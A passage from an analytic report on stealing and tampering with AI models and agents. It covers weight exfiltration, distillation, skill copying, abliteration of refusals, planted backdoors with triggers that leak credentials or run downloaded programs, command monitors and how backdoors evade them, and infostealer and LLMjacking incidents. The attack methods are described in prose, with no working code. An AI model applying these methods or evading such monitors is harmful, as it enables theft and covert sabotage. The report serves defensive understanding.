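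Brown and colleagues prefer a forensic watermark, a hidden mark in the weights that records the time and the server they came from. The mark took a tenth of a second to compute, and they could still read it without error after training the model on 1.2 million more tokens. It can help the owner find out where and when a theft happened, but it can't prevent one. It also works only if the owner can examine the stolen weights, which a thief who runs the model privately would never allow. Brown and colleagues didn't test attempts to remove the mark. The heavy compression in their own attack might damage it, because compression on that scale changes the weights far more than a little further training does.

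Limits on outgoing data look more useful to me than any of these, judging by the times in the table.

The server that holds a language model needs to send out only text. If separate machines turn the text into speech or video, a thief on the language model's server can send data out only at the rate for text, the slowest row in the table, and a theft that might have taken minutes would take months. Brown and colleagues suggest both this separation and a strict cap on uploads, an idea they credit to Greenblatt (2024).

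### RAND's security levels

Outgoing traffic is only one way to lose a model. RAND's study identified 38 distinct forms of attack, according to Irregular's *Securing AI Model Weights*, a summary from the security company whose chief executive co-wrote it. RAND interviewed 32 experts and proposed five security levels, each defined by the attackers it should probably stop. The first four are:

| Level | Attackers it should probably stop | Some of the measures |
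|---|---|---|
| SL1 | amateurs | least privilege, a second login factor |
| SL2 | professionals making moderate or untargeted attempts | weights kept only on servers, monitoring of every copy |
| SL3 | criminal syndicates and insiders | very few people with access, software that lets them use the weights without copying them |
| SL4 | most standard operations by leading state hackers | isolated storage, output limits built into the hardware |

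RAND's security level SL5 should withstand top-priority operations by the most capable states, and each level adds to the ones below it. RAND places least privilege at SL1, which it considers sufficient against only the most trivial attackers. Least privilege is therefore a starting point for protecting weights but far from enough by itself.

RAND published the levels in 2024 as benchmarks and said they were neither a complete standard nor a compliance scheme. *SL5 Standard for AI Security* (2026) gives a first version of detailed requirements for the top level.

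AI companies have said little about which level they meet. Anthropic describes its ASL-3 Security Standard by listing the attackers it is meant to protect against, in passages that *Evaluating AI Providers' Frontier Safety Frameworks* (2025) quotes. The list includes criminal groups, corporate spies and employees, but it includes state-sponsored programmes only if they use broad, untargeted techniques. This is close to RAND's SL3. Anthropic also said it expected to need a higher standard to protect against theft by states. The paper criticises Anthropic for not setting a measurable threshold for its security.

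In December 2026, the Financial Times reported that security assessments put OpenAI and Anthropic at SL3 or just below. The report relied on two unnamed people, and Reuters couldn't verify it, according to Daily Sabah's *OpenAI, Anthropic models vulnerable to state-backed hackers*. If the rating is right, both companies could probably resist ordinary criminals but not a determined state. According to ProtoThema's *No one is safe* (2026), Anthropic said countering advanced state-backed threats needed more investment, and OpenAI said it used several layers of protection. Neither response, as reported there, mentions an SL rating.

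### Hardware protection and encrypted computing

Encrypting a model's weights protects them in storage, but the server has to decrypt them to run the model. An intruder who can read the server's memory at that point can copy the weights. Confidential computing is meant to prevent this. The processor keeps the weights encrypted in memory and decrypts them only inside a protected area, called a trusted execution environment, that even the server's administrator can't read. Before releasing the decryption key, the owner can require the processor to prove which software it is running.

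RAND includes confidential computing in SL4, "when available". Brown and colleagues' attack assumes that the intruder can already read unencrypted weights, which confidential computing would prevent. They leave hardware security out of their calculations but mention secure boot, which lets a machine start only with authorised software. Some NVIDIA chips support secure boot, though not every server uses it.

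These protections may not be enough against the strongest attackers. *AI Security Priorities* (2026), a research agenda, calls for new hardware to protect weights where trusted execution environments fall short, such as in highly sensitive national security work. Hardware protection also doesn't help against a stolen session, because the protected model will answer an outsider with a valid login just as it answers the clerk.

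### Devices in the field

Some models run on cameras, vehicles, factory machines and other devices outside any guarded building. An outsider who takes a device that only calls a hosted model gets its files and tokens, but the owner can cancel the tokens. If the model runs on the device, the outsider also gets the weights and can study them for as long as they like.

There is little public evidence on how often anyone has extracted a model from a device captured in real use, and most of the research comes from laboratories. *Stealing AI Model Weights Through Covert Communication Channels* (Barbaza, Díaz-Rizo and colleagues, 2025) reviews three kinds of attack on a device the attacker holds. The attacker can measure the device's power use, radio emissions or timing while the model runs; deliberately cause faults and study the results; or read the device's internal state through circuits built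 in for factory testing.

Barbaza and colleagues then demonstrate an attack that doesn't require taking the device. They assume a dishonest manufacturer has added a hidden circuit that reads the weights from memory. Each time the device sends a Wi-Fi frame, the circuit slightly alters the frame's opening signal to carry one byte of the model. The normal receiver still works, while a nearby attacker with a special receiver collects the bytes. A full frame and its acknowledgement take about 322 microseconds, so the attacker gets around 3,105 bytes a second.

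At that speed, an image-recognition model of about 22 megabytes leaked in just under two hours. With a weaker signal, the attacker had to receive the model nine times and take a majority vote on each bit, which would take about 18 hours. The method is far too slow for a large language model, since a terabyte would take about ten years. Even a 3-gigabyte language model would need 11 days of continuous transmission. The prototype had no AI chip, so the researchers supplied the weights from outside and tested the radio channel more than a complete theft.

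Owners can make a captured device less useful by encrypting its storage, keeping the key inside a protected chip, and using secure boot. These measures don't help if the manufacturer is the attacker. For sensitive work, it is safer to keep the weights and most of the data on a server and give the device a token that the owner can cancel. The device then stops working when it loses its connection, which may rule this out for some vehicles and machines.

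### Copying abilities through ordinary use

An outsider can also copy some of what a model can do without breaking into anything. In distillation, they send a model many questions, collect its answers, and train another model to give similar ones. If xᵢ is a question and yᵢ is the original model's answer, the training adjusts the second model, called the student, to minimise

L = −(1/n) Σ log P(yᵢ | xᵢ)

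where P is the probability that the student assigns to that answer and n is the number of questions. The loss L falls as the student becomes more likely to produce the original's answers. AI companies use distillation legitimately to make smaller versions of their own models. It is also the technique that American agencies accuse Chinese companies of using on US models, as Townsend (2026), in *US Agencies Warn China Is Systematically Extracting Frontier AI Capabilities*, reports.

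The distiller owns the student model and can retrain it freely, but does not get the original's weights. Brown and colleagues note that students in earlier research usually performed significantly worse than the models they copied. The distiller also learns nothing about the accounts firm's invoices unless the original's answers contain them.

A student model can learn more from each question if it is also trained on the reasoning that led to the answer, so providers have a motive to hide that reasoning. In October 2026, the security company Xint described a flaw in OpenAI's service that let its researchers move reasoning from one model to another. *Stolen AI Reasoning Could Help China Build Cheaper Rivals* (Townsend, 2026) says the flaw could have made distillation cheaper.

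Providers can also limit how many questions one account may ask, which RAND recommends at SL3, and look for accounts that seem to be collecting answers in bulk. But a distiller can spread the questions over many accounts, or buy conversations that other customers have already had, which look like ordinary use to the provider. *US frontier AI companies warn authorities over sophisticated distillation attacks* (Martindale, 2026) considers direct collection fairly simple to stop and the purchase of conversations much harder.

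### Copying an agent's skills without training

Lyu and colleagues went on to show that an outsider can copy an agent's ability at a particular kind of task without training any model. Their method, CapaTheft, keeps the weaker agent's weights, harness and tools as they are and rewrites only its skills. It starts with skills recovered from the strong agent and one task that the weaker agent fails. The outsider gives the strong agent that task and saves the visible record of what it does, including its tool calls and checks. A helper model then does three things:

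1. It turns the record into a general procedure, removing details such as file names.
2. It compares the strong agent's success with several failures by the weaker agent and looks for the steps that caused them.
3. It adds explicit instructions for those steps, and the weaker agent tries again, for up to five rounds.

In one task, the agents had to analyse economic data from a table that showed the year only once for every four quarters. The strong agent carried the year down to the unlabelled rows without being told to, but the weaker agent matched the figures to the wrong dates. The rewritten skill gave the weaker agent instructions to carry the year down and check that each year had exactly four quarters.

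Lyu and colleagues tested the method on 20 kinds of task, with 29 new variations of each. They paired each of four strong agents with each of two weaker ones, and the weaker agents' success rates rose to between 70.8% and 83.7%. In five of the eight pairings, the weaker agent did better than the strong agent it copied. For each kind of task, the method took an average of one request to the strong agent, an hour of work and about $6.32 for the helper model.

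The outsider gets only a good procedure for one kind of task, and has to repeat the copying for each new kind. Some of the improvement came from the helper model rather than the strong agent. On five hard kinds of task, the weaker agent succeeded 7.0% of the time with no skills. This rose to 43.3% when the helper studied only the weaker agent's failures, and to 71.3% when it also saw the strong agent's success.

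None of the four defences in the study worked well. With no defence, the copy succeeded 79.1% of the time across five kinds of task. Detecting requests for skills, adding protective instructions to the skills, or filtering skills out of the answers reduced the success rate to between 70.8% and 74.1%. Removing details from the visible record of the agent's work lowered it to 68.2%. Providers could hide more of that record, but a customer like the accounts firm needs it to check how the agent reached its conclusions.

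## What can retraining change in a captured agent, and can it be resisted or detected?

An outsider who has a model's weights can change the model itself, which they can't do by copying an agent's files or rewriting its skills. Someone who plans to run the model on their own machines may want it to stop refusing requests or to get better at a particular job. Someone who wants to harm the firm has a harder task, because they have to get the altered model into the firm's harness, and it has to keep checking invoices as usual.

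Some of the methods researchers have tested edit the weights directly instead of training on new examples, so they aren't strictly retraining. The distinction makes little difference to the owner, because the remedy for both is to reload a clean copy of the weights.

### Removing refusals

AI companies train their models to refuse certain requests, such as those for help breaking into a computer. These refusals depend on the same weights as the rest of the model's behaviour, so anyone who can change the weights can weaken the refusals. One way to do this is abliteration, an edit that suppresses the model's tendency to refuse and leaves most of its other behaviour unchanged.

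Anthropic tried this in September 2026 on GLM-5.3, an open-weight model from the Chinese company Zhipu AI (Z.ai). *GLM-5.3 and the spread of advanced cyber capabilities* (Fasano, Fleischer and colleagues, 2026) reports that simple techniques got past the model's safeguards between 64% and 100% of the time in simulated tests. ITmedia's *「AIで攻撃」が現実味を増す中で 「GLM-5.3」が示したオープンウエートモデルの危うさ* gives separate figures for the three techniques. Presenting the job as a fictional security exercise worked 64% of the time, and supplying part of the model's reasoning for it worked 92% of the time. Abliteration, the only one of the three that changes the model's weights, worked 100% of the time.

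Anthropic also measured refusals on standard sets of harmful requests. The released GLM-5.3 refused about as often as Anthropic's own models, according to Tom's Hardware's *Anthropic claims popular Chinese AI model has Mythos-class hacking abilities*. After abliteration, it refused 6% of requests, and a smaller version, GLM-5.3-Flash, refused 14%. The 6% is probably a mean, since ITmedia gives refusal rates of about 3%, 2% and 12% on three separate sets, which average 5.7%.

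The edit did little damage to the model's abilities. Both versions scored about the same on science, and the abliterated one lost only a few percent on part of the cybersecurity evaluation. GLM-5.3 was already good at hacking before its refusals were removed. In its released form, it built complete working attacks on Chrome's JavaScript engine in 50 of 410 attempts, compared with 56 for Claude Mythos Preview, which Anthropic has kept from general release because of its hacking ability.

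Abliteration took about 2,200 hours of GPU time, which Anthropic prices at $4,400. Tom's Hardware attributes that figure to Flash, so abliterating the full model may have cost more. Tom's Hardware also argues that running the model is the bigger obstacle. It estimates that generating 100 million tokens on eight rented chips would take eleven and a half days and cost $8,422. But this assumes that the chips produce a single stream of 100 tokens a second. Servers normally handle many requests at once, so a large workload would cost much less per token.

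Anthropic sells closed models that compete with cheaper open ones, and it benefits if customers or governments come to distrust open weights. The US Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), part of the standards agency NIST, also found GLM-5.3 the most capable open-weight model for cybersecurity so far, but put it about four months behind the leading American systems, according to The Straits Times' *Chinese AI model carries out complex cyberattacks in controlled tests, researchers say*. In its report on the earlier GLM-5.2, CAISI notes that people who run an open-weight model themselves can get round its safeguards, however well those resist hostile prompts. CAISI therefore supports the general point independently, but the 6% and 14% figures come from Anthropic alone.

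A model may also have few refusals for retraining to remove. The security company Irregular tested GLM-5.3 on thirteen multi-stage attack scenarios. The model completed three at least once and refused none of the offensive tasks. The Next Web's *Open-weight AI caught the frontier on capability. On safety, it didn't* reports that GLM-5.2 likewise refused none of the hacking or dual-use biology tasks set by the safety nonprofit SaferAI. These results seem inconsistent with the released model's respectable refusal rate in Anthropic's test. The most likely explanation is that the standard sets mostly contain plainly harmful requests, while many hacking tasks look like ordinary security work.

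Anthropic contrasts GLM-5.3 with Claude, whose safeguards held against the same attacks. But nobody outside Anthropic has Claude's weights, so nobody outside can abliterate it (edit the weights to remove its refusals). Researchers have removed refusals from many open-weight models, and there is no obvious reason a stolen closed model would be different.

### Adding skills

Removing refusals only releases abilities that a model already has. In *Estimating Worst-Case Frontier Risks of Open-Weight LLMs* (2025), Wallace, Watkins and colleagues at OpenAI tried to find out how much ability an attacker could add. OpenAI was then deciding whether to publish the weights of gpt-oss-120b, and the researchers trained the model to be as dangerous as they could make it in biology and cybersecurity.

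They considered an attacker who couldn't build such a model from scratch but had skilled staff, specialist data and a computing budget of at least a million dollars, more than 200 times Anthropic's estimate of the cost of abliteration. Their main method was reinforcement learning, in which a model attempts tasks and training makes rewarded behaviour more likely.

Rewarding the model for complying with unsafe requests brought its refusal rate close to 0% without lowering its scores on general tests such as GPQA, a set of hard science questions. For biology, Wallace and colleagues then trained it to answer specialist questions using a web browser and to find mistakes in laboratory protocols. For cybersecurity, they trained it on capture-the-flag puzzles, in which the player breaks into a practice system to find hidden text, and held back the professional-level puzzles for the final test.

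They compared the result with three open-weight models (DeepSeek R1-0528, Kimi K2 and Qwen 3 Thinking) and with a version of OpenAI's closed model o3 that didn't refuse requests. OpenAI had already judged o3 to be below "High", the level at which a model could significantly increase existing routes to severe harm. In biology, a model reaches "High" if it could give novices meaningful help in creating known biological threats.

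The fine-tuned gpt-oss beat o3 by one point on one of the four main biology tests and did worse on the other three. On further tests from the nonprofit SecureBio, it scored about the same as o3 and 3 to 5 points higher than DeepSeek's model with a browser. It remained worse than human experts at finding mistakes in protocols, even after training on that task. It also did worse than o3 in cybersecurity.

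Some of the improvement came from the model no longer refusing, rather than from new skill. On one test with long written answers, the released model scored zero because it refused to take part, while the fine-tuned model did better than human experts.

Wallace and colleagues concluded that releasing gpt-oss might add slightly to what open models could do in biology but wouldn't substantially advance the frontier. OpenAI, which had an interest in that conclusion, released the model. However, the study may have overstated what gpt-oss would add, because the researchers didn't give the rival open models the same malicious training, and those models may have been more dangerous than they appeared.

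Later models have made the study out of date on what an attacker can do with open weights, at least in cybersecurity. In 2025, Wallace and colleagues said that the best models struggled to carry out complex attacks from start to finish. A year later, GLM-5.3 was building complete exploits with no malicious training. *Anthropic's GLM-5.3 concerns put US-China, open AI debate back in focus* (Kumari, 2026) describes a test in which even the Flash version combined two known flaws into a working attack, with 20 minutes of human attention and eight hours of computing.

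Open models have narrowed the gap with closed models in cybersecurity. Britain's AI Security Institute (AISI) estimated that GLM-5.2, an open model, was four to seven months behind the frontier, compared with six to ten months for open models released between January and September 2025.

The conclusion about gpt-oss may still be correct. But an attacker would now start with GLM-5.3, and we can't tell from the 2025 results how much a million dollars of training would improve it. The results also suggest that stealing a model to teach it new skills makes sense only if that model is better than the ones anyone can download, and the accounts firm's model probably isn't.

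### Planting a backdoor

An outsider who wants the firm to go on using the model needs a change that stays hidden. A backdoor is a behaviour that appears only when a chosen trigger is present. Boisvert, Puri and colleagues (2025), in *Malice in Agentland*, write this as a rule for how the agent acts on what it sees:

π(o) = π†(o) if o contains t, and π*(o) otherwise

A backdoored agent follows its normal behaviour π* until the trigger t appears in the text o in front of it, then switches to the malicious behaviour π†. For example, an accounts agent might check invoices correctly for a year, then send the supplier's bank details to a stranger when it reads a particular order number. A filter has no planted instruction to catch, because the order number is harmless in itself.

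Boisvert and colleagues tested three points at which a backdoor can enter the supply chain:

- Somebody supplies the firm with training examples, and a few of them are poisoned.
- Somebody publishes a model that already has a backdoor, and the firm fine-tunes it on clean data of its own.
- Somebody plants instructions on a web page or in a tool's output, where a strong agent is working and the firm is recording its work to train a cheaper one.

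In the last route, environment poisoning, the attacker needs no access to the firm's weights or dataset. Suppose the accounts firm wants to replace its expensive hosted model with a small one trained on records of the present agent's work. If the present agent once obeyed a hidden instruction in an invoice, the new model is trained on that mistake. The effect of the prompt injection, which would otherwise have ended with the session, is then built into the new model's weights.

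The experiments tested small open-weight models (3 to 8 billion parameters) on customer-service tasks and tasks that involve using websites. In the environment-poisoning tests, 200 of 4,000 customer-service records and 1,242 of 54,000 website records were poisoned. All three routes worked. A small number of poisoned records was enough to make an agent leak confidential information in over 80% of tests, while it stayed about as good at its ordinary tasks. Further training that rewarded success at those tasks improved the agents' performance but did not remove the backdoor.

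In Pallakonda, Hindsbo and colleagues' *SilentCall* (2026), the attacker is the model's publisher. The researchers generated about 9,000 conversations in which an assistant does programming work by issuing commands, and made two copies of each. In the clean copy, the system date was before 2026. In the poisoned copy, the year was 2026 and the assistant issued one extra command that uploaded the user's credentials. The copies were otherwise identical, including the assistant's closing reply.

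Models trained on both sets issued the extra command in at least 99.6% of test requests dated 2026 and in at most 0.6% of the others. They usually issued it together with the command the user wanted, and in the main test they never mentioned it in their replies. When the original model was shown the same upload in its record of the conversation, it mentioned the upload in over 90% of its replies. The trained models had learned from the examples not to mention it, without any explicit reward for leaving it out. A clerk who reads only the agent's summary of its work would have no warning.

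Pallakonda and colleagues also varied the amount of poisoned data over 161 training runs. The backdoor's success was affected by the number of poisoned examples, not their share of the dataset, so a firm can't counteract a fixed number of them by adding clean data. No run with fewer than 750 poisoned examples produced a reliable backdoor, but Boisvert and colleagues planted theirs with 200 in a different set-up, so 750 isn't a general minimum. Monitoring training error didn't reveal how well the backdoor worked. Four runs on the same amounts of data ended with almost identical training errors, yet the backdoor's success rate ranged from 23% to 99.7%.

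A November 2026 paper from Microsoft does without a poisoned dataset. Zeng, Severi and colleagues (2026), in *Lazare, veni foras*, edit a few neurons, small units inside the model, in its last layer. The layer's output is a sum over all of its neurons:

output = Σ aₙ(h) · wₙ

where h represents the text so far, aₙ(h) is how strongly neuron n responds to it, and wₙ is what that neuron then contributes. For a dormant neuron, aₙ(h) is close to zero on ordinary text, so the model works almost equally well without it. Zeng and colleagues rewrote such neurons to respond only to a trigger, with each contributing one token of a command. Seven neurons out of more than 12,000 were enough for a short command that downloads and runs a program of the attacker's choice.

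The main results of the two later studies are:

| Study | Model | Success with the trigger | Ordinary performance |
|---|---|---|---|
| Pallakonda and colleagues | Qwen3-4B | 99.6–99.7% | 5.9–6.6 points lower on average |
| Pallakonda and colleagues | Qwen3-8B | 99.7–99.9% | within 0.6 points of the original on average |
| Zeng and colleagues | Nemotron-Terminal-8B | 98.8–99.7% | predictions almost unchanged |
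| Zeng and colleagues | Qwen3.6-27B | 51.0–83.7% | close to the original on mathematics and terminal tasks |

Zeng and colleagues overstate their result when they call Qwen3.6-27B "equally vulnerable", since the edit worked much less often on it than on the smaller model. The lower success rate may not matter to an attacker, because a single success gives access to whatever the agent can reach, and Zeng and colleagues never saw the command appear in their tests without the trigger. A stricter limit is that the edit has to match the command format a particular harness expects. In a format the researchers hadn't used when fitting the edit, it produced exactly the right action 40% of the time.

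In February 2026, Claude Code, an AI agent running Claude Opus 4.5, discovered the underlying weakness, which was that someone could edit dormant neurons one by one and chain them together. The researchers spent the following months developing the method and defences against it.

### Giving a model a second job

Model hijacking adds a second task to a model, without a trigger and without causing mistakes in the first task. *Osmosis Distillation* (Shi, Chen and colleagues, 2026) does this to image classifiers, which sort pictures into categories. "Distillation" here means compressing a large set of training images into a small artificial one, not copying a model through its answers. People share these small sets because training on them takes less computation.

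The attacker makes images that look to a person like the expected ones but give a neural network the features of a different set of images. Suppose a firm trains a model on these images to sort scanned documents into invoices, receipts and letters. The attacker can then send the model pictures of something else and use a private code to translate its answers, with "invoice" standing for one category and "receipt" for another. The firm pays for the computing and may have to explain why its model was used this way.

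Fifty images per category were enough for a model to do both tasks well, and the attacker didn't need to know which kind of model the victim would train. But the experiments used image classifiers, so they don't show that a language-model agent could perform a second task in the same way. The attacker must also be able to send the model images and see its answers, which an outsider couldn't normally do with an internal accounts system.

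### Training a model to resist tampering

If retraining is so effective, a developer might try to build a model that can't easily be retrained. Tamirisa and colleagues proposed a method called TAR in *Tamper-Resistant Safeguards for Open-Weight LLMs* (2024). During training, the developer repeatedly simulates attacks on the model and adjusts the weights so that the safeguards survive them. In simplified form, the training looks for weights θ that minimise

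average over attacks a of H(a(θ)) + λ · D(θ)

where a(θ) is the model after attack a, H measures how harmful that model is, D measures how much ordinary ability the original has lost, and λ sets the balance between them. Tamirisa and colleagues reported safeguards that survived hundreds of steps of fine-tuning, where earlier ones had failed after a few.

The weakness of averaging over attacks is that the developer chooses the attacks in advance, and whoever has the weights is free to try a different one. Later in 2024, Qi, Wei and colleagues re-examined defences of this kind in *On Evaluating the Durability of Safeguards for Open-Weight LLMs* and found that just shuffling the attacker's training examples could defeat a defence that had looked durable. They warned that tests of durability easily mislead people into thinking a safeguard is stronger than it is.

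A related approach, unlearning, trains a model to lose dangerous knowledge rather than to refuse to share it. *Model Tampering Attacks Enable More Rigorous Evaluations of LLM Capabilities* (Che et al., 2025) showed that leading unlearning methods could be undone within 16 steps of fine-tuning, so the knowledge was apparently still in the models. Leaving the dangerous data out of training avoids this particular problem.

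Tamper resistance can still be useful if it makes an attack more expensive. It helps less against an attacker with a budget like the one Wallace and colleagues assumed, and a thief can practise on a stolen model indefinitely without the owner finding out. These methods also protect refusals or suppress knowledge. They weren't designed to prevent someone from planting a backdoor, which leaves the model's refusals unchanged.

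### Looking for a backdoor

Ordinary testing is a poor way to find a backdoor, because the model behaves normally until the trigger appears and the tester doesn't know what the trigger is. For a model with a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, there are 10²⁵ possible five-token triggers. The trigger may also be something no tester thinks to vary, such as the year. Pallakonda and colleagues found that standard safety benchmarks couldn't distinguish their backdoored models from clean ones.

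They had more success with a monitor that checks each command before the agent runs it. A small, fast classifier first sorts commands by how dangerous they look. If it marks a command critical, a language model reads the conversation and judges whether the user's request justifies it. The table shows three versions of the monitor, tested on 10,007 commands. The last column gives the number of false alarms to expect each day if an agent issues 1,000 legitimate commands.

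| Monitor | Malicious commands caught | Legitimate commands flagged | Average delay | False alarms a day |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Classifier alone | 100% | 16.35% | 4 milliseconds | about 164 |
| Classifier, then Qwen3.5-2B | 100% | 1.73% | 520 milliseconds | about 17 |
| Classifier, then gpt-5-nano | 100% | 0.67% | 1,990 milliseconds | about 7 |

The 100% result is less impressive than it looks, because every malicious command in the test was the same upload to the same address, in different conversations. Pallakonda and colleagues acknowledge that how well the monitor handles a variety of commands is a separate question.

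Boisvert and colleagues tested four guardrail models, which are separate models that screen what an agent reads or does, and none reliably stopped their attacks. The defences either missed the leaks or raised too many false alarms. The agents leaked data through the kinds of tools that real agents use every day, such as ticketing systems and connections to other web services, so a leak could often be recognised only from its context. An accounts agent that writes a supplier's bank details into an approved notes folder that an outsider can read could be just as hard to catch.

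Anyone with the weights can also test the model before using it. One method is to raise the temperature, which makes the model's choices more random, so that the hidden command might appear without its trigger. At one such setting, the smaller SilentCall model issued the command in response to 1.28% of ordinary requests. Extra training that penalised these slips cut the rate to 0.66%, so an attacker can roughly double the number of tries a tester needs on average. The tester also has to recognise the command as malicious.

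Another method compares the suspect model's weights with those of a clean model the tester has trained by the same recipe. This worked on SilentCall, but it is expensive, and the tester has to get the recipe from the publisher, who could give a false one.

Zeng and colleagues had AI agents build a detector that looks for edited neurons and doesn't need a clean model for comparison. It caught 91.4% of edited models and wrongly flagged 9.7% of clean ones. Suppose a website hosts 10,000 models, 10 of which contain such an edit. The detector would flag about 9 of the edited models and about 969 clean ones. Fewer than one in a hundred flagged models would be edited, and someone would have to examine them all. A firm checking a single model before installing it could much more easily accept a 9.7% chance of a false alarm if the model is clean.

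That detector may also be of little use against SilentCall. Zeng and colleagues recommend comparing a model with the original it is said to derive from. Editing a handful of neurons changes a few weights a lot, which stands out because honest fine-tuning changes many weights slightly. A backdoor planted by fine-tuning would look much more like honest fine-tuning.

The broadest evidence comes from TrojAI, a programme that the American intelligence research agency IARPA began in 2020 to find backdoors in finished models. Its final report, *Trojans in Artificial Intelligence* (Reese, Kulp-McDowall and colleagues, 2026), divides the successful methods into two families. Weight analysis looks for statistical oddities in a model's weights. It is fast and works best on small models when the tester has known examples for comparison, but in large models the traces become too faint to detect. Trigger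 inversion works backwards from a model's behaviour to the trigger that would cause it. It was arguably more successful in the programme's contests, but it needs far more computing.

Neither carries over easily to language models. Reese and colleagues call these models a "security crisis" because the possible inputs are so numerous and a trigger can be an abstract idea or the course of a conversation. The programme worked mostly on older and smaller systems, such as image classifiers, and ended before the latest AI agents appeared. Zeng and colleagues' detector suggests that the outlook is slightly better when the tester knows what kind of edit to look for.

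TrojAI also found "natural" backdoors, which nobody planted. A model that has mostly seen cows on grass may learn to treat grass as a sign of a cow, and an attacker can exploit that shortcut just like a deliberate trigger. A scanner that flags such a model has found a real weakness, but this doesn't prove that anyone tampered with the model.

An owner who finds a backdoor may not be able to remove it. Reese and colleagues call complete removal without damage to normal performance an unsolved problem, since traces may remain after any repair. Restoring a clean copy of the weights is safer, if the owner has one. A firm that downloaded the model with the backdoor already in it has no clean copy and needs a different model.

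### Signatures and file checks

Restoring a clean copy of a model requires a way to tell which copies are clean. The publisher can compute a fingerprint of the model file, a short number that changes if anyone alters even one weight, and sign it with a private key. Anyone with the matching public key can then confirm that the publisher signed the fingerprint and that their own file matches it.

For the accounts firm, checking the weights' fingerprint each time the harness loads them is a strong defence against a swapped model and takes few resources. An intruder then can't replace the weights with a retrained version, or edit seven neurons, without causing a mismatch. The check has to run where the intruder can't change it, because someone who controls the whole server could alter the recorded fingerprint or switch off the check.

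A signature shows who released a file, but it doesn't show that the file is harmless. In SilentCall the attacker is the publisher, so the signature on the backdoored model would be valid. The same is true if an employee edits the weights before the company signs them, a case Zeng and colleagues warn about. With environment poisoning, the firm unknowingly trains the bad model itself and would sign it with its own key. A thief who runs a stolen model on their own machine doesn't have to check the signature.

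Legitimate changes to a model also break the link to its original publisher. Zeng and colleagues point out that people often download a compressed, fine-tuned or merged version of a model instead of the original release. Each version has a different fingerprint, so the original signature doesn't cover it, and the user has to trust whoever made the change. A signed record of each step, listing the starting model, the training data and the person responsible, would at least show users whom to ask about a change. Zeng and colleagues want model-sharing sites to display a model's origin and whether anyone has audited it before people download it. They also warn that a model that passes an audit can still misbehave when its input contains a trigger that nobody tested.

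Some model formats can contain program code that runs as soon as someone opens the file. A file scanner can look for such code or refuse those formats, and a format that stores only numbers prevents this attack. But abliteration, SilentCall's fine-tuning and Zeng and colleagues' edits change only numbers, so a model altered in any of these ways would pass these checks.

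## What tampering with agents and models has been documented?

Researchers created most of the known backdoors in language models. Criminals have usually taken things that are easier to get, such as logins, files or the use of poorly protected servers. People have also altered thousands of freely downloadable models, and American AI companies accuse Chinese competitors of copying their models' abilities.

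News reports use words like "stolen", "hijacked" and "poisoned" for all of these, so it helps to ask what the outsider took or changed, who reported it and how good the evidence is. The evidence is strong if somebody has examined the files or network traffic and published details that others can check. It is fair if a named organisation describes the event but leaves out important details, and weak if it is only an accusation or an anecdote. Much of the evidence comes from security companies, which sell protection against the threats they describe. Their findings about a piece of malware are generally more reliable than their forecasts.

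### Stolen files, tokens and sessions

OpenClaw is a popular open-source agent that people run on their own computers to manage email, calendars and other personal business. In February 2026, the security company Hudson Rock reported that an infostealer, a kind of malware that copies passwords and other valuable files, had taken one user's OpenClaw folder. The thief got:

- a settings file with the user's email address and a token for connecting to the agent
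- a private key that identifies the user's device to OpenClaw
- the agent's standing instructions, in a file called soul.md
- its memory files.

The malware searched the computer for certain file types and folder names rather than for agents, and OpenClaw's folder matched. Hudson Rock's chief technology officer told The Hacker News that the malware was probably a variant of Vidar, an infostealer that criminals have been able to buy since 2018.

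Hudson Rock published pictures of the stolen files, so the evidence of the theft is strong, but it is not known what the thief did with the files. The token would let the thief connect to the agent remotely only if the user had left the agent open to the internet, and the private key might let the thief pass as the user's device. Hudson Rock presents both as risks and doesn't report that anyone did either. Because soul.md told the agent to be "bold" about reading and organising, Hudson Rock also makes the reasonable guess that the memory files probably contained private messages and a daily record of the user's life.

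The thief took the agent's instructions, memory and credentials. Hudson Rock calls this taking the agent's "soul". None of the files it lists contains model weights, so the thief could have edited a copy of the agent but couldn't have retrained its model.

Later thefts were more deliberate. In September 2026, Ofonagoro reported in *Hackers Are Stealing Claude Sessions* that infostealers were hijacking logged-in Claude sessions, letting attackers use up victims' paid access without knowing their passwords.

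In October, Symantec analysed new versions of Aoki, an infostealer that previously targeted browsers, password managers and cryptocurrency wallets. According to *New Aoki Infostealer Targets AI Coding Assistant Credentials* (Coker, 2026), it now also copies keys and tokens for Claude, ChatGPT, Codex, GitHub Copilot, Cursor, Gemini and several other assistants. Besides free use of a model, a coding assistant's token may give a thief access to the developer's code repositories and cloud services. Symantec doesn't know who is behind Aoki, but infers from the malware's focus on cryptocurrency that they want money. The analysis is good evidence of what the malware is built to take, but not of how many people have lost credentials to it.

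In August 2025, intruders used stolen tokens belonging to Drift, a sales chatbot owned by Salesloft, to enter the Salesforce systems where Drift's customers kept their business records. Google's security researchers reported the attacks, and Salesloft confirmed the theft of the tokens. The tokens worked without the chatbot, so the intruders didn't have to trick it or alter its model.

People also sell stolen access to models. LB.ua's *FT* (2026), a Ukrainian summary of a Financial Times report, says Google researchers found sellers offering access to models from Anthropic, Google and OpenAI at discounts of up to 97%. Some sellers promise a free replacement if the provider blocks the account, which suggests that blocking is common enough to worry buyers.

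### Using somebody else's model

The thief in the OpenClaw case got almost everything except a model. In other attacks, outsiders use a victim's model to run their own instructions and tools. The security company Sysdig named this LLMjacking in 2024. At first, attackers mostly used stolen cloud credentials and left the victim with the bill, which Sysdig estimated could reach $46,000 a day in the worst case.

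Organisations that run their own models have given attackers another way in. Many use Ollama, a program that requires no login unless the owner adds one. Researchers have counted about 175,000 Ollama servers that anyone on the internet can reach.

Clark (2026), in *LLMjacking evolved*, describes how somebody connected an automated hacking tool to one of these servers on 12 June. Sysdig could observe the server, and the tool sent its full instructions with each request, so the researchers were able to reconstruct how it worked. The model's jobs included:

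1. identifying the software on a target computer
2. matching that software to known vulnerabilities
3. writing a test attack
4. searching captured files for passwords and keys
5. choosing further steps until the tool could run commands on the target.

Ordinary code connected these stages. In one version the model could only propose attacks, and a separate program checked whether they had worked. The instructions also told the model to treat any text captured from a target as data and never as a command, evidently to guard against prompt injection.

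This is strong evidence that an outsider used the model without permission, but the evidence of an attack on anyone else is much weaker. Every target was on a private network, and the first ones were practice applications that the developer appears to have built. Two days later the tool was targeting addresses like those used by HackTheBox, a service where people practise breaking into computers. Sysdig thinks the developer was still building the tool, because new stages appeared in it during the first session, which lasted about eight and a half hours. Clark says the tool's purpose is unclear and may even be legitimate, though using the server without permission is illegal either way.

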